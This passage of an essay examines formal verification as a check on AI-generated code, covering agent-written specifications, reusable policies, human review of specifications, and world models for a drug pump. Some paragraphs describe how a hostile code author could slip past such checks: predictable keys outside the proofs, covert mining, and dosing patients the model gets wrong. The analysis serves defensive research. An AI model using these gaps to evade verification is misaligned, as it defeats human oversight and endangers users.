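An AI agent wrote the specifications under human guidance. *DeepMind AlphaProof Code* (Ganglani, 2026) reports that human experts reviewed every specification before separate agents began searching for proofs. Lean's kernel then checked each proof against the approved specification. Because the specifications were approved first, a prover that got stuck could not make the theorem easier.

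Even so, a 26,000-line specification is a lot to review. It is longer than the 16,700 lines of Rust in the SymCrypt verification project, so reading a specification is not always quicker than reading code. But part of the specification describes the processor, and other projects could reuse that part and test it against real chips.

EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026) describes a useful test of the specification. The team restored two historical bugs in test versions of the program and proved that each one violated a security theorem, so the theorems were strong enough to rule out at least those two bugs. The agents also flagged about 1% of the code for closer human review.

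The theorems make different assumptions about the attacker. One group of proofs covers attackers with ordinary computers and relies on stated assumptions about the underlying cryptography. A separate proof shows that the handshake stays secret from a future attacker with a quantum computer. That proof is symbolic, meaning it treats operations such as encryption as perfect and considers only how an attacker could combine them.

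According to EconoTimes, the proofs did not cover all of libsignal, and the verified program was a small command-line tool that uses the library for one-to-one conversations. The proofs also excluded key generation. This would matter a great deal if the program's author were hostile, because the program could choose predictable keys that let the author read every message and still follow the rest of the protocol perfectly. Ganglani adds that the project did not check for crashes or memory leaks.

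None of the four properties, as cryptographers usually define them, covers timing. The attacker in these definitions can read and change network traffic and sometimes steal keys, but doesn't measure how long the phone takes. A model of machine code would still be a good starting point for constant-time proofs, because it already includes branches and memory addresses. A proof about the machine code would also cover any leaks the compiler introduced.

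### Policies chosen once

DeepMind's specifications apply to one protocol, and few programs justify that much expert attention. An alternative is to choose a policy once and apply it to many programs, as in Necula's proof-carrying code.

In 2024, Parnian Kamran, Premkumar Devanbu and Caleb Stanford adapted this idea to language models under the name "proof-carrying code completions". The user chooses a safety policy, and their tool attaches a precondition to every function that could break it. A function that reads files might start like this:

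```
method Read(path: string) returns (text: string)
  requires StaysInside(path, "/payroll")
```

Each time generated code calls `Read`, the model has to prove that the path stays inside the payroll folder. If the path comes from an untrusted source, the proof fails unless the code first checks the path. The user writes no logic and can check the proof on an ordinary computer. In a case study, the tool's first attempt produced Dafny code that provably avoided one common way of escaping a folder. The Python code that GPT-4 generated for comparison had no such guarantee.

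The empty-table payroll method would also pass this check, because it reads no files. That is acceptable in a policy meant only to prevent harm. A bigger concern is that someone has to list all the dangerous functions. If the list misses a function that can open files, and that function has no precondition, code can use it to open files outside the folder.

Later projects added reusable policies, including the no-crash theorems for the 239 fuzz harnesses and TACIT's protection of classified data. *PerMIT* (2026) proves a reusable guarantee for AI agents that keep a long-term memory, which an attacker might try to corrupt. Its main theorems hold whatever strategy the agent follows. By one of them, the agent performs the same operations and gives the same replies in runs under different attacks, provided the transcripts of those runs meet certain conditions.

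An operating system can enforce a policy on an even wider range of programs. The company Proofcraft announced in *seL4 security proofs now complete on AArch64* that it has completed the seL4 kernel's secrecy proof for 64-bit Arm processors. The proof covers the applications that run on the kernel, though the owner still has to decide which information flows to authorize.

Published standards can also serve as shared specifications. In the SymCrypt project, AI agents help translate cryptographic standards into Lean. But Ho and colleagues report that the translation still needs expert design and review. The effort is worthwhile because anyone who implements the same standard can reuse the Lean specification.

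Security rules that depend on what a program is for are hard to write in advance as part of a reusable policy. For example, "Only the author of a comment may delete it" makes no sense for a program without comments. This is less of a problem for rules about files, network connections, memory or running time, which many programs share. An owner can therefore combine a general policy with a few task-specific conditions, such as which department averages the payroll function may publish.

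An error in a shared policy affects every program that relies on it. But a shared policy justifies more review and more testing against harmful programs than a specification for one program does, so it is likely to contain fewer errors.

### Can developers check a specification?

Someone has to confirm that a specification is the right one, however it was produced. Livshits doubts that developers will do this well. People who generate code by chatting with a model often "accept all changes" without reading them, and they may be just as careless when a verification system asks them to approve specifications, settle ambiguities and investigate failed proofs. He argues that the person will be the least reliable part of the process unless all of it is automatic.

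One of Livshits's examples is Astrogator, which asks users to confirm a request in a language precise enough for verification but close to ordinary English. In a test with 1,260 programs for 21 tasks, it verified 83% of the correct programs and identified 92% of the incorrect ones. This is a good result, but it leaves about one correct program in six for a person to review. The study of 802 developers also supports his concern, because human reviewers increasingly approved changes without comment.

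*The Specification Spectrum* argues that a complete formal specification of a messy real-world application is often longer and harder to write than the program. It also argues that programmers work out what they want as they write code, whereas people who ask a model for code may never do that thinking. The post recommends proving only the parts that justify the effort, and using types and tests for the rest.

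Other researchers accept that specifications are hard to write and want better tools to help people express them. A tool might infer likely rules from existing code, let people click through a program and describe what each part should do, or generate examples of unusual behavior for people to accept or reject. On this view, the problem is mainly interface design, and few companies that build AI provers are working on it.

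Here is how such a tool could work for the payroll function. Suppose the specification does not cover departments with only one employee. The tool finds two programs that both meet the specification but behave differently, and shows the user the difference:

- Program A reports the legal department's average salary as 120,000. The department has one employee.
- Program B leaves the legal department out of the report.

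The user picks one, and the tool adds a condition to the specification. Each question is concrete, and the user never has to read a formula. After each answer, the tool can search for another pair of programs that behave differently. If no such pair exists, the specification allows only one behavior. In most applications, users would get tired long before that point, so the tool would need to ask about the differences that matter most.

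This method can reveal only the behavior that the program model includes. If the model leaves out timing, none of the questions will cover timing. Users may also answer badly, for example by approving two monthly averages that together reveal a salary. A tool could look for attacks of this kind and show the user their consequences, but only if the attacks are already known.

Livshits's own solution is to apply security constraints while a model generates code, for example by making it add a bounds check to every array access. Developers then don't have to approve each specification, but someone still has to choose the constraints, much like setting a policy once. The disagreement is therefore mostly about rules specific to one application. Experiments could help settle it by giving developers faulty specifications, with and without such a tool, and counting how many they approve.

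### Requirements that resist formal statement

Some requirements are hard to formalize however much help people get. Suppose a company's payment program sends 5,000 to a supplier on its approved list. The supplier may have delivered the goods, or may be a friend of the program's author who delivered nothing. The program's trace is the same in both cases, so a specification over these traces cannot forbid the fraudulent payment without also forbidding the legitimate one.

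The company can add delivery records to the model and require one for each payment. The author's friend then has to forge a record, which makes fraud harder but does not rule it out. The company could also require a second person's approval or limit the size of payments. These rules are easy to state formally and reduce the opportunities for fraud, but they do not define fraud.

Formal methods can sometimes rule out harm without identifying a malicious purpose. A program that satisfies noninterference can't leak a salary, either deliberately or accidentally. Purpose matters when the same action can be useful or harmful. An agent allowed to email customers can send an honest reminder or a misleading one, and a payroll program can use spare computing steps to mine cryptocurrency instead of sorting. A specification that fixes the exact output and sets a tight resource limit leaves little room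 for such misuse, but nobody can write out every email in advance.

In other cases, the harm depends on facts about the outside world. For example, a specification might require that a program controlling a hospital pump never deliver more than 60 mg of a drug per hour. This limit is a simple property of single runs, and a monitor can enforce it. But whether that dose is safe depends on the patient's body and the other drugs the patient is taking, and the program may have no access to that information.

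"Unintended" is difficult to specify for a different reason, because it depends on what somebody wanted as well as on what the program does. If a user asks an agent to "clean up the payroll folder" and it deletes last year's records, the deletion may be a disaster or what the user had in mind. If the user never thought about those records, there may have been no intention for a specification to capture.

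A frame condition avoids this problem by forbidding unlisted changes rather than unintended ones, so the agent may change only the files on a list. This is precise and often easy to check, but it forbids harmless changes that nobody thought to list, such as creating a temporary file. The agent could instead ask before it deletes anything, so that the user has to decide whether they want the deletion. But a user who gets too many requests may start approving them without reading them.

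### Modelling the outside world

In 2024, David Dalrymple and colleagues proposed a more ambitious approach, which they called "guaranteed safe AI". It has three parts. A world model describes mathematically how an AI system's actions affect the outside world. A safety specification states which effects are acceptable. A verifier then proves that, if the world model is right, the system's effects will be acceptable, or at least bounds the probability that they will be.

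The hospital pump shows what this adds. Let c be the concentration of the drug in the patient's blood in milligrams per liter, u the pump's rate in milligrams per hour, V the volume in liters through which the drug spreads, and k the fraction of the drug that the body removes per hour. A simple world model is:

dc/dt = u/V − kc

Suppose that the concentration starts at zero and must never exceed 20 mg per liter. At 20, the drug would enter at a rate of u/V and leave at a rate of 20k, so the concentration can't rise above 20 as long as u ≤ 20kV. If every patient has k ≥ 0.1 and V ≥ 30, then 20kV is at least 60, so proving that the software never runs the pump above 60 mg per hour also proves that the patient's concentration stays within the limit.

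The proof also covers a range of patients, so doctors don't need exact values of k and V. Dalrymple and colleagues want world models to express uncertainty in ways like this. But a patient with failing kidneys might have k = 0.02. With V = 30, a rate of 60 mg per hour would bring the concentration close to 60 ÷ (0.02 × 30) = 100 mg per liter, five times the limit. The program would still meet its specification, and the proof would still be valid for the model.

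Critics think such errors are unavoidable in the situations that matter most. Andrew Dickson argued in 2024 that formal guarantees about AI systems in the physical world can at best cover rough approximations of their behavior. A useful model may also need measurements that nobody can take, such as the exact condition of a patient's organs. People are even harder to model, and no equation like the one for the pump predicts how a customer will react to an email.

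Errors in the world model are more dangerous when the code's author is hostile. If the model is wrong about one patient in a thousand, carelessly written software will usually harm few people, but software written to do harm could search for those patients and give them the highest dose the specification permits. The proof therefore needs a model that is right even in the worst case.

Supporters can reply that engineers already rely on models to design bridges and aircraft, and that an explicit model is easier to inspect and correct than a developer's unstated assumptions. The model can also be narrow, since the pump needs a model of only one drug. The pump can measure the drug's concentration and stop if the reading differs too much from the prediction. This would protect the patient with failing kidneys if the sensor is reliable and the pump stops in time.

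This makes world models promising for narrow physical tasks with well-understood science and good sensors. They are much less convincing as a way to prove that a general-purpose agent will do no harm, because the model would have to cover everyone and everything the agent might affect. Reviewing it would also be far more work than reviewing the 26,000 trusted lines behind the Signal proofs. For most AI-generated code, limiting the program's access to the outside world is easier than modelling what it could do there. For example, a payroll function that can only read a list of records and return the averages needs no model of the economy.
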